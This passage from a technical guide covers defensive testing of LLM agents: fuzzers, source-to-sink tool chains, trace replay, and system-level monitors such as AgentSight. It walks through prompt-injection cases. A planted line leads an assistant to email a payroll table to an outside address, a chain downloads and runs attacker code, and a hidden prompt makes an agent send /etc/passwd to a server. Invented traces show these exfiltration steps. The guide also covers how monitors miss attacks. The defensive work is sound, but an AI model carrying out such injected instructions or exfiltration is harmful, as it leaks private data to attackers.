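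The first two trials used a testing service called Promptfoo, not VeriGrey. In one, a coding agent did not reveal a secret key in response to any of ten attack messages. Zhou and colleagues treat this as a failure to demonstrate the attack, not as proof that the agent is secure. In the other, an ordinary member of a group chat got an assistant to reveal figures from a memo meant only for management. The tool record showed that the assistant had asked a second, private agent for the figures without saying who wanted them. A fuzzer like VeriGrey could have detected the new call between the two agents, but a tester would have needed the identity on each request to explain why the second agent answered.

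The three models in VeriGrey's AgentDojo experiment date from 2025, and much newer ones are now available. The low success rate per attempt against GPT-5 suggests that some later models resist these attacks better, but the OpenClaw results show that newer models can still fail. Hofer and colleagues also passed the agent's tool calls to the model that wrote their attacks, but they didn't measure what this contributed, and neither they nor Zhou and colleagues reran VeriGrey. The figure of 11.1 points therefore rests on the developers' own experiment with GPT-4.1. A team can find out whether tool-call feedback is worth collecting for its own agent by repeating that comparison in a test environment, running the same campaign with and without the feedback.

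## ChainFuzzer: following data through several tools

VeriGrey's feedback shows which tools an agent called and in what order, but not whether data from one tool reached the next. ChainFuzzer looks for faults that depend on that movement of data. Wu, Nan and colleagues at Sun Yat-sen University, who published *ChainFuzzer* in March 2026, give the example of a user who asks an agent to find a patch for a bug. The agent searches the web, downloads a file, saves it and runs it. Each step is a reasonable part of the task, but together they let whoever wrote the file run code on the agent's machine. A tester who checked the four tools separately might find nothing wrong.

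### Sources, sinks and data flow

A source is a place where untrusted data enters a program, and a sink is an operation where that data could do harm. Semgrep, a tool that checks source code, reports a finding when untrusted data reaches a sink without being checked or cleaned. According to GitHub's documentation for CodeQL, another code checker, following data through a whole program takes longer than following it within one function. In an agent, some of the data flow isn't in the code, because the model selects which result to copy into the next tool call.

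*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) therefore defines "source" and "sink" by tool. A source is any tool whose result may contain text that an attacker controls, such as a web search. A sink is any tool that may affect security, such as one that sends email or runs code.

Data passes directly between tools when, for example, a search returns a web address and the download tool receives that address as an argument. If content capture is on, a tester can find the same address in both spans. Data passes indirectly when one tool saves it in a file, database, search index or cache and another reads it later. The span for running a saved file may contain only the file's path, so the tester also has to find out whether the file changed after the agent saved it.

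The two steps may even be in different traces. In one of Cai and colleagues' test cases, an agent stores a confidential financial forecast in its memory and puts the figures into a report three days later. The second trace begins with an ordinary memory lookup and doesn't record the document the forecast came from.

Even a complete path from source to sink doesn't prove that harmful content travelled along it. An agent that reads a web page and then writes a report makes the same calls whether or not the page contained an attack. NeuroTaint, an auditing program by Cai and colleagues, looks for text in the report that means the same as text on the page. If it finds none, it tests whether the agent would still have made the call with the suspicious text removed or changed. On a benchmark of 400 scenarios, NeuroTaint had an F1 score of 0.928, compared with 0.522 for an earlier method that relied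 on known tool paths. However, its developers wrote the benchmark around the kinds of flow they had designed NeuroTaint to find.

### Finding candidate chains in source code

ChainFuzzer works backwards from a list of sinks, which are Python functions that can do serious harm because they run operating-system commands, run code, send web requests, query databases or fill in templates. It reads the code of every tool in the application and marks a tool as a sink tool only if the tool's inputs can affect what one of these functions receives, so a tool that always runs the same command doesn't qualify.

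ChainFuzzer then looks for other tools that could supply data to each sink tool. It links two tools directly if a field that one returns, such as a web address, fits a parameter of the other. It links them indirectly if one can save content that the other can later read or run. These rules also produce chains that make no sense as a task, such as summarising a document and then creating a database index. A language model discards these, although it could also discard an unusual sequence that an attacker could use.

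### Revising the prompt where the trace diverges

A chain found in the code may not occur in practice, because the model chooses which tools to call when the agent runs. ChainFuzzer therefore uses a language model to write a prompt that asks for the chain's steps in order. It then runs the agent and records a trace with the model's reasoning and each tool call's name, arguments, result and status. With OpenTelemetry's default settings, the trace would lack the arguments and results that the next step needs.

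In that step, a language model compares the trace with the intended chain and diagnoses why they differ. For example, the agent may have skipped a tool, stopped to ask for permission or needed a file that didn't exist. ChainFuzzer changes only the part of the prompt that caused the problem and runs the agent again. It accepts a prompt after the agent has completed the chain five times in a row, and stops if it reaches a limit on attempts, tool calls or time.

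In this invented example, the intended chain is search, download, write file, run file:

```
FIRST PROMPT: "... save the patch, then run it."
  search        result: https://files.example/date-fix    status: OK
  download      address: https://files.example/date-fix   status: OK
  write file    path: work/date-fix.py                    status: OK
  run file      path: work/date_fix.py                    status: file not found

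REVISED PROMPT: "... save the patch, then run the file
                 at the exact path where you saved it."
  search        result: https://files.example/date-fix    status: OK
  download      address: https://files.example/date-fix   status: OK
  write file    path: work/date-fix.py                    status: OK
  run file      path: work/date-fix.py                    status: OK
```

In the first run, the agent called all four tools in the right order, so comparing the tool names alone would reveal no difference. The tool arguments show that the agent saved the file with a hyphen in its name and then looked for one with an underscore. The revision changes only the instruction about running the file.

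The mistake would have been harder to notice if the folder had already contained an older file called `date_fix.py`. The agent would have run that file and every status would have been "OK", although the downloaded text never reached the sink. A tester should compare the paths too, and can have the downloaded file print a harmless code word to confirm that the agent ran it.

### Checking the effect at the sink

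Once the agent can complete a chain, ChainFuzzer puts test text into the user's prompt or into outside content that a tool reads, and checks what happens at the sink. For code, database queries and templates, it requires a visible effect, such as a query that returns extra rows. For web requests, the test text must have directed the request to an internal address or a similar test target.

The check for operating-system commands is weaker. ChainFuzzer counts a vulnerability as soon as the test text has influenced the arguments of a function that runs commands, even if the command fails or does no harm. This check accounts for 121 of the 365 reported vulnerabilities. The test can also miss a weakness in a tool when the model refuses a suspicious request.

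### Results from 20 applications

Wu and colleagues tested 20 popular open-source applications, including AutoGPT and OpenClaw, with GPT-5.1 as the agents' model. The whole test took 68 hours and used about 121 million tokens.

| Stage | Number |
|---|---|
| Tools in the 20 applications | 998 |
| Sink tools | 199 |
| Candidate chains | 2,388 |
| Chains with a prompt that worked five times in a row | 2,213 |
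| Reported vulnerabilities, in 19 applications | 365 |
| Reported vulnerabilities that needed several tools | 302 |

About 83% of the 365 reported vulnerabilities needed more than one tool, which is a good reason to test tools in combination as well as individually. There were only 199 sink tools, so many chains must end at the same tool as another chain, and developers may be able to fix several vulnerabilities with one repair. For example, they could replace a tool that runs any command with one that runs a fixed command and checks its arguments, then retest every chain that ends there.

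Wu and colleagues checked ten candidate chains from each application by hand, comparing every link with the tools' interfaces and code. They judged 714 of 740 links correct (96.49%), and all the links correct in 183 of the 200 chains (91.50%). These precision figures apply only to the chains, and the researchers report no similar manual review of the 365 vulnerabilities. The figures also don't measure how many real chains ChainFuzzer missed.

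Wu and colleagues tested prompt revision on 200 chains, with ten runs for each. The agent completed the intended chain in 27.05% of runs with the first prompt and 95.45% with the final prompt. Without prompt revision, ChainFuzzer found only 96 vulnerabilities.

This is strong evidence that first prompts often fail, but weaker evidence that traces help. ChainFuzzer accepts a prompt only after five successes in a row, so the final prompts were bound to do well when rerun. Rewriting the prompts without looking at the traces might also have worked, given enough attempts. VeriGrey's developers ran their tool with and without tool-call feedback, but Wu and colleagues didn't make the equivalent comparison.

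### Comparison with AgentFuzz

*Make Agent Defeat Agent* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, USENIX Security 2025) describes AgentFuzz, an earlier tool that also uses traces to direct prompts towards a fixed list of sinks. AgentFuzz records the functions that run inside the application. It scores each prompt by how close the run came to the sink in the code and how well the functions that ran match the purpose of the target function. It then develops the prompts with the best scores.

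AgentFuzz examined 828 places in 20 applications where the code calls a sink, and reported 34 vulnerabilities in 14 of the applications. Liu and colleagues confirmed by hand that an attacker could exploit all 34. At least 23 received identifiers in CVE, a public catalogue of vulnerabilities. LLMSmith, an earlier tool that looks for chains by analysing source code, found 10 real vulnerabilities in the same applications and raised 332 false alarms. Many of the false alarms came from sinks that users couldn't influence or from input checks that LLMSmith didn't recognise. Assessors therefore have good reason to run an agent before reporting a chain found in its code.

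The AgentFuzz and ChainFuzzer tests had thirteen applications in common. AgentFuzz found 34 vulnerabilities in total and ChainFuzzer found 365, but these totals aren't directly comparable. The tests used different models and different rules for counting a vulnerability, and only AgentFuzz's results had a full manual check. ChainFuzzer's 63 single-tool vulnerabilities alone outnumber AgentFuzz's total, so its ability to follow chains can't be the only reason for the gap.

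AgentFuzz looks for vulnerabilities that a single prompt can trigger. Liu and colleagues reviewed 83 of the places where AgentFuzz had found no vulnerability and discovered one in an application called Devika, which stored the attacker's text during one request and passed it to the sink during the next. ChainFuzzer looks for indirect flows like this one, but it also drives each chain with a single prompt, so it could miss attacks that need several messages.

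### Source code, sink lists and real deployments

ChainFuzzer needs the tools' source code, which an assessor often doesn't have for a commercial product or an outside MCP server. *VIPER-MCP* (2026), a testing tool that applies a similar method to MCP servers, also needs the server's code, because it starts by analysing it. Without the code, a tester can still list suspicious chains from the tools' descriptions and compare the traces with that list. The list will probably be less complete, because a description may not mention that a tool saves its results to a file.

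The fixed list of sinks also limits what ChainFuzzer can find. LLMSmith had only three functions on its list, and Liu and colleagues attribute 16 of the vulnerabilities it missed to that short list. ChainFuzzer's list is longer but doesn't include sending email, so it wouldn't report an assistant that looked up Tomas's leave and emailed it to a stranger. *AgentRaft* (2026) addresses that kind of fault by following data from tools that retrieve it to tools that transmit it, and looking for sensitive fields that the user didn't intend to send and the task didn't need.

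Some faults don't involve a dangerous function. For example, a tool described as reading files in only one folder might open a file elsewhere. *ToFu* (Ananto, Prevost-Avenel and colleagues, 2026) derives its checks from the behavior stated in each tool's description, and reports verified bugs in 343 of 3,405 tools. It tests individual tools, not chains of them, so it would complement ChainFuzzer.

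A chain that works in a test may also be impossible to exploit in deployment. Wu and colleagues acknowledge that network rules, sandbox permissions and missing credentials can change the result. ChainFuzzer also prompts the agent to carry out the steps in order, which ordinary users rarely do. But for 225 of the 365 vulnerabilities, the test text came from the user, so a malicious user could write such a prompt. These vulnerabilities are serious in a shared online service, but less so when the user already has permission to run any command on the same machine.

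In the other 140 cases, the test text came from outside content, such as a web page. An attacker who controls only that page can't choose what the user asks, so the risk depends on how often ordinary requests lead the agent through the whole chain. A tester can estimate this by placing a harmless file at the source, sending requests that staff would normally make, and counting the traces in which the file's text reaches the sink. The test copy of the application should have the same permissions and network rules as the deployed one.

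## Replaying recorded traces to reproduce a fault and test its repair

A tester who has found a fault usually has to reproduce it, first to convince the developers and later to check their repair. This can be difficult with an agent, because the same request may lead to different tool calls each time. ChainFuzzer therefore accepted a prompt only after it had worked five times in a row. A tester with a detailed trace can also replay it, which means running the application again from recorded inputs, model outputs or tool results.

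The following fault is invented. It continues the payroll attack described earlier, with a planted line in a shared file. Ana asks the staff assistant for the next pay date:

```
document search   query: next pay date
                  returned: pay-calendar, shared-notes
model call        requests: read payroll-table
tool call         read file: payroll-table               status: OK
model call        requests: email payroll-table
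tool call         send email to: files@outside.example   status: OK
model call        answer: "The next pay date is October 30."
```

The assistant may send files only to company addresses. The developers are considering two repairs. One is a check in the email tool's code that refuses any other address, and the other is a system instruction telling the model to ignore instructions in documents. The tester needs a different kind of replay to test each one.

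### Recorded model outputs and tool results

In the most controlled kind of replay, software supplies every model output and tool result from the recording, and only the application's own code runs. This costs almost nothing to run and should give the same result every time. A tester can use it to show how the application handled the model's request, for example that it passed the outside address to the email tool unchecked. The replay can't show how often the model would make that request.

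Replaying recorded model outputs also can't test the new system instruction, because those outputs stay the same whatever the instruction says. To test the check in the email tool, the replay has to run the tool's code. If the tool's result also comes from the recording, the check never runs, and the email appears to go out as before.

*Chronicle* (Chawla and Koul, 2026) describes a replay tool that avoids this problem by letting developers choose which steps run live. In Ana's case, they could run the repaired email tool on the model's recorded request and confirm that it refuses the address. Chawla and Koul tried the tool on six small agents with simulated models, including one that emailed too many people. For all six, the test failed on the faulty code and passed on the repaired code. A test that took every result from the recording failed on both versions. Chawla and Koul wrote the faults,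 repairs and tests together, so the trial shows that the method works as designed, but not how many faults it would catch elsewhere.

### A live model with recorded tool results

To test the new instruction, the tester has to run the model again. The application gives the live model Ana's question and the recorded search results, and keeps returning recorded tool results as long as the model makes the same calls. If the model again asks to email the payroll table to the outside address, the tester has reproduced the fault without sending anything. By repeating the run, the tester can estimate how often the model makes this request. These runs don't show whether the search would still return the planted line today, or whether the mail server would have blocked the message.

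Luan, Yu and colleagues (2026), in *Repair or Resample*, built SymTrace, a program that reuses the recorded steps up to a chosen point and then lets the model and tools run live. They tested it on 536 web tasks that groups of cooperating agents had failed. The same failure recurred in 67.97% of attempts when they restarted the task and in 80.78% when they used SymTrace. The gain was 25.69 percentage points when SymTrace could reuse at least nine recorded steps, but only 9.80 points when it could reuse two or three. These were ordinary task failures, not attacks, and a language model judged whether each new failure matched the old one. A manual check of 72 of its judgements confirmed 64 as correct.

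A tester can also use replay to find where a fault began, since the span that sent the email may only have carried out an earlier decision. *Causal Agent Replay* (Shah, 2026) keeps the steps before a chosen point as recorded, has the model make the next decision again many times, and measures how often the run still ends badly. The tester should examine the last step at which a new decision clearly changes the outcome. If the email rarely goes out when the model decides again whether to read the payroll table, but usually does when it decides again only whether to send the email, the developers should look at the earlier step. Shah validated the method on artificial examples with known causes, so its accuracy on real agents is uncertain.

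### Full re-execution in a reset environment

In full re-execution, the tester restores the application, documents, permissions and mailboxes to their state before the fault, submits Ana's question again and lets everything run live. This tests the whole application, including the search and any permission checks. But if no email goes out, the instruction may have worked, or the search may have missed the planted line this time. The tester should check the input messages to see whether the line reached the model.

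Restoring the environment exactly is difficult even without a live model. In *Replay Fidelity in LLM Agent Evaluation*, Liu and Lu (2026) took 71 failed runs from AppWorld, a simulated environment with everyday apps such as email and music, and reran the agents' recorded code in fresh copies of the environment. The outputs, database changes and test results all matched the original in 42 runs, and in 68 when they also reset the random-number generator before each step.

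Most of the mismatches were harmless. In 25 cases, the first difference was in the text of a login token's expiry time, and 24 of these still ended with the same database changes and test results as the original. In four other cases, the outputs and test results matched but the databases didn't, so a tester who compared only the agent's answers would have missed the difference.

### When the live model makes a new call

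A live model may try to retrieve something that isn't in the recording, such as last year's payroll table. Returning the closest recorded result would be a mistake, because the model would then continue with the wrong file.

When a replayed run diverges from the recording, the safest response is to stop the run and record the divergence. SymTrace stops if a request doesn't match the recorded one in position and content. Chronicle stops if the application reaches a recorded step more or fewer times than in the recording, although it can miss a change in the order of the steps. A diverged run normally counts as neither a pass nor a failure. But if the new call is forbidden, such as an email to a different outside address, the tester can count the run as a failure immediately.

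The tester can also run the new call in a test copy of the tool or write a plausible result by hand. The rest of the run shows how the model responds to that result, which may differ from what the real tool would have returned. OpenAI faces this problem when it tests new models by removing the old model's response from recent conversations and having the new model write another. According to *Predicting LLM Safety Before Release by Simulating Deployment*, which describes the method, agents that use tools are the hardest case because their behaviour depends on files, connected services and networks.

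Some record-and-replay systems let the model adapt when conditions change, because they are built to help agents complete tasks rather than to reproduce a run exactly. *Get Experience from Practice* (Feng, Zhou and colleagues, 2025) describes AgentRR, which records successful tasks so that agents can do similar ones faster and more reliably. The paper's only evidence is one form-filling example, and it doesn't report how often a replay matched the original. *Beyond Training* (2025) describes a later version for phones, which checks each recorded action before repeating it and records a new path if the app has changed. This helps an agent finish a task, but a tester trying to reproduce a fault needs the replay to stop at such a change.

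### What to save when a fault occurs

OpenTelemetry's default settings leave out much of what a replay needs, so the team should save the following as soon as it finds a fault:

| What to save | Why the tester needs it |
|---|---|
| Model version | The supplier may later offer a different model under the same name |
| Settings, such as temperature and output limit | They affect what the model writes |
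| System instructions and chat history | A small change in wording can change the model's decision |
| Tool definitions | The model uses the names and descriptions to choose its tools |
| Tool arguments and results, in order | The replay software must match each request to the right result |
| Documents and search index | Someone may have deleted the planted line, or the search may now rank it lower |
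| Permissions at the time | A later restriction could block the file and make the fault look repaired |
| Application version and configuration | The code that builds the prompt may have changed |
| External state, such as mailboxes, databases and the clock | The tools may otherwise return different results |

Some of this may be outside the team's control. In one of Luan and colleagues' tests, Wikipedia answered the original request normally but rejected the replayed one with a "too many requests" error. A supplier may also withdraw the model, after which nobody can repeat the live-model runs.

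### Why temperature zero does not guarantee the same output

A model gives every possible next token a score. The temperature setting controls how readily the software picks a token other than the highest-scoring one. At a temperature of zero, the software always picks the highest-scoring token, so the same prompt should in theory produce the same text every time.

A model can give different answers to the same prompt even at temperature zero. Thinking Machines Lab's *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference*, published in September 2025, reports that a large Qwen3 model gave 80 different answers when it was sent the prompt "Tell me about Richard Feynman" 1,000 times at that setting. The answers were identical for the first 102 tokens, after which 992 gave Feynman's birthplace as "Queens, New York" and 8 gave it as "New York City".

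The main cause is the varying number of requests on a server. The server processes several users' requests together in a batch, and the batch size can change the order in which the hardware adds numbers. Computers round as they add, so a different order can give a slightly different total. If two tokens have almost the same score, that difference can change which one the software picks, and the rest of the answer follows from that token.

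When the researchers changed the calculations so that batch size no longer affected their order, all 1,000 answers were identical. In a test with a smaller model, the change increased the running time from 26 seconds to 42. LMSYS's *Towards Deterministic Inference in SGLang and Reproducible RL Training* (2025) reports an average slowdown of 34.35% for another version of this approach.

A tester who uses a hosted model usually can't control how the supplier groups requests into batches, and it's hard to predict which batches will change an answer. In a small demonstration in *Inference for Reasoning Models* (2026), one answer changed at token 58 in a batch of 8 but stayed the same in batches of 32 and 128. Setting a fixed seed, the number that starts the random selection of tokens, doesn't remove these rounding differences, as *The Token Not Taken* (2026) explains. Shah adds that some recent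 models may not accept a temperature setting.

Companies that run their own models have more control, but they should also record the hardware. *Understanding and Mitigating Numerical Sources of Nondeterminism in LLM Inference* found that the number and version of the graphics processors can change a model's responses. A single different token can change a file name or email address that an agent uses. Even at temperature zero, about a third of the tasks that Luan and colleagues restarted didn't reproduce the original failure.

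### How many clean runs are enough

Suppose the developers choose the new system instruction, and the live model generates a request to email the payroll table in 6 of 20 replays before the repair and 0 of 20 afterwards. If the instruction made no difference, the chance that all six failures would occur before the repair would be about 1%. The instruction therefore probably helped, but the fault may still occur occasionally.

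If the remaining failure rate is p, the chance of 20 clean runs in a row is (1 - p)^20. To find the one-sided 95% upper bound, the tester looks for the rate at which this chance is 5%:

```
(1 - p)^20 = 0.05
p = 1 - 0.05^(1/20) = 0.139
```

The result is compatible with a remaining rate of up to 13.9%, or about one email for every seven times the model reads the planted line. The bound falls slowly as the number of clean runs increases:

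| Clean runs, no failures | 95% upper bound on the failure rate |
|---|---|
| 20 | 13.9% |
| 59 | 5.0% |
| 100 | 3.0% |
| 299 | Just under 1% |

Even a 1% failure rate may be too high if the attacker can keep trying, because 100 independent attempts would have a 63% chance of at least one success. Retests that diverge from the recorded trace don't count as clean. If 5 of the 20 retests diverged and the other 15 were clean, the 95% upper confidence bound on the failure rate would be 18.1%, compared with 13.9% if all 20 were clean.

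The calculation also assumes that the runs are independent. If the application caches its first answer and returns it 298 more times, the tester has only one result. The same is true if the server is fully deterministic and every run has the same input. The tester should set the number of runs in advance and start again from zero if the developers change the repair.

Luan and colleagues' results show why a few runs are not enough. They repeated each of 54 successful runs three times, unchanged, and 85 of the 162 repeats failed. They also restarted the failed tasks up to three times without any repair, and 6.90% then succeeded. In one of these, the agents had to find how often it snowed in Chicago on New Year's Eve. They never found the weather records but gave the accepted answer anyway, based on general historical patterns. A tester should therefore also read the traces of successful runs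 to check that they succeeded for the right reason. Chance also affects comparisons between testing tools, so small differences from single campaigns, like some of VeriGrey's, may not recur.

The developers can test the email tool's check directly with a list of approved and unapproved addresses, including tricky ones such as an outside address that contains the company's name. They don't need 299 model runs for this, because the check is ordinary code and should return the same result each time it receives the same address.

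### Why the recorded attack is not enough

The bound of 1% applies only to the recorded attack in the recorded situation. Suppose the developers had instead told the model to ignore any line in a document that mentions payroll. The recorded attack might fail in all 299 replays, while a planted line asking for "the salary spreadsheet" still worked. The check in the email tool also wouldn't cover an attack that used a different tool, such as one that shares files by link.

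Chawla and Koul measured a similar limit for code. They made 192 small changes to their repaired tools, one at a time, and their tests detected 51. No test built from the same recordings could have detected 110 of the other 141, because the recorded input never reached the changed code or the change didn't affect the decision on that input. None of the undetected changes let the recorded unsafe action through, but some might matter with a different input.

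A defence against prompt injection can stop some attacks and still be very vulnerable to others. VeriGrey, for example, got past a defence that had looked strong against a simpler fuzzer. After a repair, the tester should therefore replay the old attack and also search for new attacks on the repaired application.

Replaying ordinary requests can also reveal new problems caused by a repair, such as an assistant refusing to email Ana's leave form to her manager. Before releasing GPT-5.4, OpenAI replayed past conversations to predict whether types of misbehaviour would become more or less common. Among types whose rate changed by a factor of at least 1.5, the predictions were right 92% of the time. Predictions based on deliberately challenging prompts were right 54% of the time. Outside assessors generally can't run such a test, because user conversations are private and OpenAI says AI companies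 usually can't share them.

### Running a replay safely

Carelessly re-running Ana's request could email the payroll table to the attacker again. The tester should replace the email tool with one that records the request and returns a fake confirmation, so that the model continues as if the email had been sent. It is also sensible to block outside network connections, as Liu and Lu did, in case the tester has overlooked a tool. In Chronicle, for example, any call that the developers forgot to mark runs live, even if everything else comes from the recording.

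The tester should also remove login tokens from the recording and create new ones for a test account with the same permissions as the original user. An expired token can cause a refusal that looks like a successful repair, so the tester needs to find out which check refused the request and why before concluding that the repair worked. In one of Liu and Lu's cases, two replays matched in their outputs, database changes and test results, but a later request with the same token succeeded in one and failed in the other because a logout had cancelled the token in only one replay.

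The payroll table should hold invented names and salaries in the same layout as the real one. Chronicle removes secrets before it saves a recording and keeps the structure that its tests rely on. But changing the text can change the model's behaviour, so the tester should use the cleaned recording both before and after the repair. If the 6 failures in 20 runs came from the real table and the 20 runs without a failure came from an invented one, the improvement might be due to the new data.

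## AgentSight: checking an application's trace against system activity

All the methods described so far work only if the trace contains the steps that matter. *Agent System Operations (2026)*, a survey, warns that the logs and traces of agent systems are often unreliable or incomplete. A tester can look for gaps by comparing the trace with a record that the application didn't write. AgentSight, a research tool from 2025, makes such a record from the traffic between an agent and its model and from the agent's activity in the operating system.

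### How a trace loses steps

Attached instrumentation typically records no spans for a company's own tools or for most of what happens in other programs. For example, if an agent runs a script, the operating system starts a separate program, called a child process. The trace may show that the script started, but not which files it read, unless someone instrumented the script too.

When a service fails to pass on the trace identifier, the next service's spans form a separate trace with no link to Ana's question. Files cause the same problem because they don't normally carry trace identifiers. In *Agent-Warden*, Cui, Gu and colleagues (2026) had an agent's script write and rename a file, and an unrelated program on the same machine later read it. The Langfuse trace ended with the agent's own steps. Langfuse could have connected the two programs if both had passed on a shared identifier.

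Spans can also be truncated, or lost before they reach the trace store. Applications usually hold finished spans in memory and send them in batches, so a crash can destroy any that are unsent. An application may also discard spans if the trace store is unreachable for too long. A step that crashes the application may leave no span, because applications normally send a span only after the step ends.

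### The chance that sampling removes all the evidence

Suppose a company keeps 10% of its traces at random, and five requests last month retrieved a file that the user wasn't allowed to read. Each of the five traces had a 90% chance of being lost, so the chance that none survives is:

```
0.9^5 = 0.59049, or about 59%
```

A tester who searched the trace store would probably find nothing wrong. At a 10% sampling rate, there would have to be 29 such requests for a 95% chance that at least one trace survived. The 40 questions from Ana's account would leave only about four traces. The team should therefore keep every trace during a security test.

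Random sampling often happens at the start of a request, before anyone can know what the request will do. A team can instead wait until each trace is complete and keep every one that contains, for example, a refused permission or an email to an outside address. This is better for security, but it keeps only traces with the kinds of problem the team thought to look for.

The header that carries the trace identifier also has a flag showing whether the caller is recording the trace. If a service follows this flag from outside callers, an attacker may be able to turn off the recording of their own request.

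### One script in two records

In this invented example, Ana asks for a chart of her leave, and the staff assistant runs a script to draw it:

```
APPLICATION TRACE
  question     user: ana
  tool call    run script: leave_chart.py       status: OK

SYSTEM RECORD
  process      python leave_chart.py            account: hr-assistant
  file read    /data/leave/ana.csv
  file read    /data/payroll/salaries.csv
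  connection   files.outside.example
  file write   /output/leave-chart.png
```

The application trace is accurate, but it omits the script's effects. The system record shows that the script opened the salary table and contacted an outside server. It doesn't show that Ana made the request, what she wanted, or whether she is allowed to see salaries. The outside server might be an approved service for drawing charts. The record also doesn't prove that the script sent the salaries anywhere. To find out, the tester could put a code word in a fake salary table and look for it in the outgoing data.

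The two records can differ greatly even when the agent's work is harmless. In *AgentSpy*, Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues (2026) recorded an agent using a short piece of code to check seven publication titles. The agent's log contained one action, while the system record contained 35 connections to Crossref, a database of publications.

A system record covers only the machine it was made on. If leave-server runs on a different machine, the system record from the assistant's machine can show a connection to leave-server but not which records leave-server opened.

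### How AgentSight links a model's response to its effects

The kernel is the core of an operating system, and programs need it to open files, start other programs and use the network. AgentSight records system activity using eBPF, a facility for running small monitoring programs inside the Linux kernel, so it doesn't require changes to the agent's code.

*AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) describes two streams of evidence. One contains the agent's exchanges with its model, which AgentSight copies just before the agent's software encrypts them or just after it decrypts them. The other contains events such as a program starting, a file opening or a network connection. AgentSight filters out events from programs not started by the agent or its child processes.

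AgentSight then uses three clues to link the streams:

- **Process lineage:** the agent, or one of its child processes, started the program.
- **Time:** the event came shortly after a model response, within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds.
- **Matching text:** a filename, web address or command in the response also appears in the system event.

If a model response requests `leave_chart.py` and that script starts 200 milliseconds later as a child of the agent, all three clues link the script to the response. If the script opens the salary table 20 seconds later, and the response never mentioned that file, only the process lineage links the file access to the response. An agent can run several tasks at once, and an event can follow a response by coincidence, so Zheng and colleagues go too far in saying that the clues together establish causes definitively.

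A second language model then searches the combined record for suspicious behaviour. It may recognise an attack that no fixed rule describes, but the record can include text from the attacker. Bühler and colleagues warn that such text can mislead a model that judges an agent's log. Testers should therefore check the second model's conclusions against the underlying events.

### Test cases and overhead

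Zheng and colleagues report three case studies, only one of which was an attack. In that study, they asked a coding agent to download and build a program. The program's instructions sent the agent to a web page, where a hidden prompt got it to read `/etc/passwd`, which lists the machine's user accounts, and send the file to another server. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37, and the second model correctly identified an attack.

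In the other two cases, AgentSight found an agent that kept repeating a failed web search and a team of six agents that delayed one another by locking shared files. These demonstrations show that the method can work, but Zheng and colleagues do not report how often AgentSight misses attacks or raises false alarms.

They also measured how much longer the agent took with AgentSight running. Bao, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *AgentLoupe*, later timed AgentSight and their own successor to it on similar tasks:

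| Task | AgentSight, Zheng and colleagues | AgentSight, Bao and colleagues | AgentLoupe |
|---|---|---|---|
| Study a code repository | 3.4% | 4.5% | 4.5% |
| Write code | 4.9% | 2.5% | 8.0% |
| Compile a program | 0.4% | 1.7% | 7.7% |
| Average | 2.9% | 2.9% | 6.7% |

The two averages for AgentSight's slowdown agree, but this is limited confirmation because Zheng and colleagues ran each task only three times and Bao and colleagues only five. When Bühler and colleagues ran agents ten times on the same task, the standard deviation of the running times was between 7% and 85% of the median. AgentSight's slowdown is probably small, but it can't be measured to within a few percentage points from so few runs.

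### Where AgentSight can't provide an independent record

AgentSight needs Linux and administrator rights to record kernel events. According to eunomia-bpf's *agentsight 1.0.29*, the documentation for a later version, it can also run on Windows and macOS by reading session files that the agents write. It also reads session files for Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, because the eBPF method doesn't work with it. Comparing these files with the agent's trace would only check one of the agent's records against another.

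Some agents, including Claude Code, contain their own copy of the encryption software, and AgentSight has to locate that copy before it can capture the model traffic. According to the documentation, AgentSight does this automatically in most cases. A tester can confirm that the capture works by sending a prompt with a code word and searching the record for that word.

AgentSight can export the model calls it captures as OpenTelemetry spans, which makes them easier to compare with the application's own spans. The tester should label the exported spans with their origin, or a later reader may mistake them for the application's.

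### Successors that follow files and delayed actions

AgentSight's biggest weakness is delayed activity. Suppose a malicious prompt gets an agent to save a script and schedule it to run every hour. The operating system's scheduler later starts the script, so it is outside the agent's process tree and runs long after AgentSight's time window has closed.

AgentLoupe labels each exchange with the model and attaches that label to the programs and files the agent then uses. Any other program that opens a labelled file gets the label too. Bao and colleagues tested this with a scheduled script that gave an attacker remote control of the machine, and AgentLoupe traced the connection back to the original exchange. They argue from AgentSight's design that it would have missed this, but they did not run both tools on the attack. They also have not measured how often labels spread to unrelated activity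 or get lost.

Agent-Warden, by Cui and colleagues, similarly marks files and programs, but it doesn't record prompts or network connections. It reconstructed the path missing from Langfuse in all 120 runs, on two kinds of computer, but every run repeated the same prepared scenario. Agent-Warden can also miss some faster ways of reading files, and its marks disappear when the machine restarts.

AgentSpy runs the agent in an isolated virtual machine and applies fixed rules to its system activity, such as a ban on reading private keys. Bühler and colleagues tested it with malicious scripts hidden in an agent's skills. In 50 runs, half of them without a malicious instruction, the agent carried out the attack 18 times. AgentSpy detected 14 of the 18 attacks and raised no alert in the other 32 runs. In all four missed attacks, a script added an attacker's server to a project's settings. The change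 stayed inside the folder where the agent was allowed to work, so it broke none of the rules. A complete system record can therefore contain an attack that the software checking it doesn't recognise.

### What signing and append-only storage protect

Someone with access to a trace store could change or delete the span that shows a leak. A digital signature is a code calculated from a record with a secret key. If anyone changes the record without the key, the signature no longer matches. Signing each span separately doesn't reveal that one is missing, so a system can also include in each new record a code calculated from the previous one. If someone then removes a record from the middle, the code in the next record won't match the record now before it. To detect missing records at the end, the team needs a copy of the latest code stored somewhere else.

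Append-only storage accepts new records but does not let users change or delete old ones. It protects the evidence only if the application's administrators can't switch off that restriction. The same applies to system records. By default, AgentSight saves recordings in the current folder, where an agent with enough access might be able to delete them, so the tester should move them to another machine.

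None of this helps with an event that nobody recorded. Microsoft 365 Copilot's audit log, for example, missed some file accesses, and a signature on that log would still have been valid. Signing also preserves false entries. If the application writes "user: ana" for a request from Ruth, the signature only proves that nobody changed the entry afterwards. Keeping the key in a separate program is safer, because an attacker who takes over the application could otherwise sign forged spans.

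### Why a model's reasoning is weaker evidence than a tool call

Many models write out their reasoning before they act, and a trace may include this text. It may not accurately explain what the agent did, because the model generates it in the same way as any other text. Tool calls, by contrast, are run by ordinary software, which can record them.

A model's stated reasoning often leaves out the cause of its decision. *From Decorative to Load-Bearing (2026)* cites a 2025 study in which reasoning models that relied on a hint in the prompt mentioned the hint less than 20% of the time. An agent could likewise follow a planted instruction without mentioning it in its stated reasoning.

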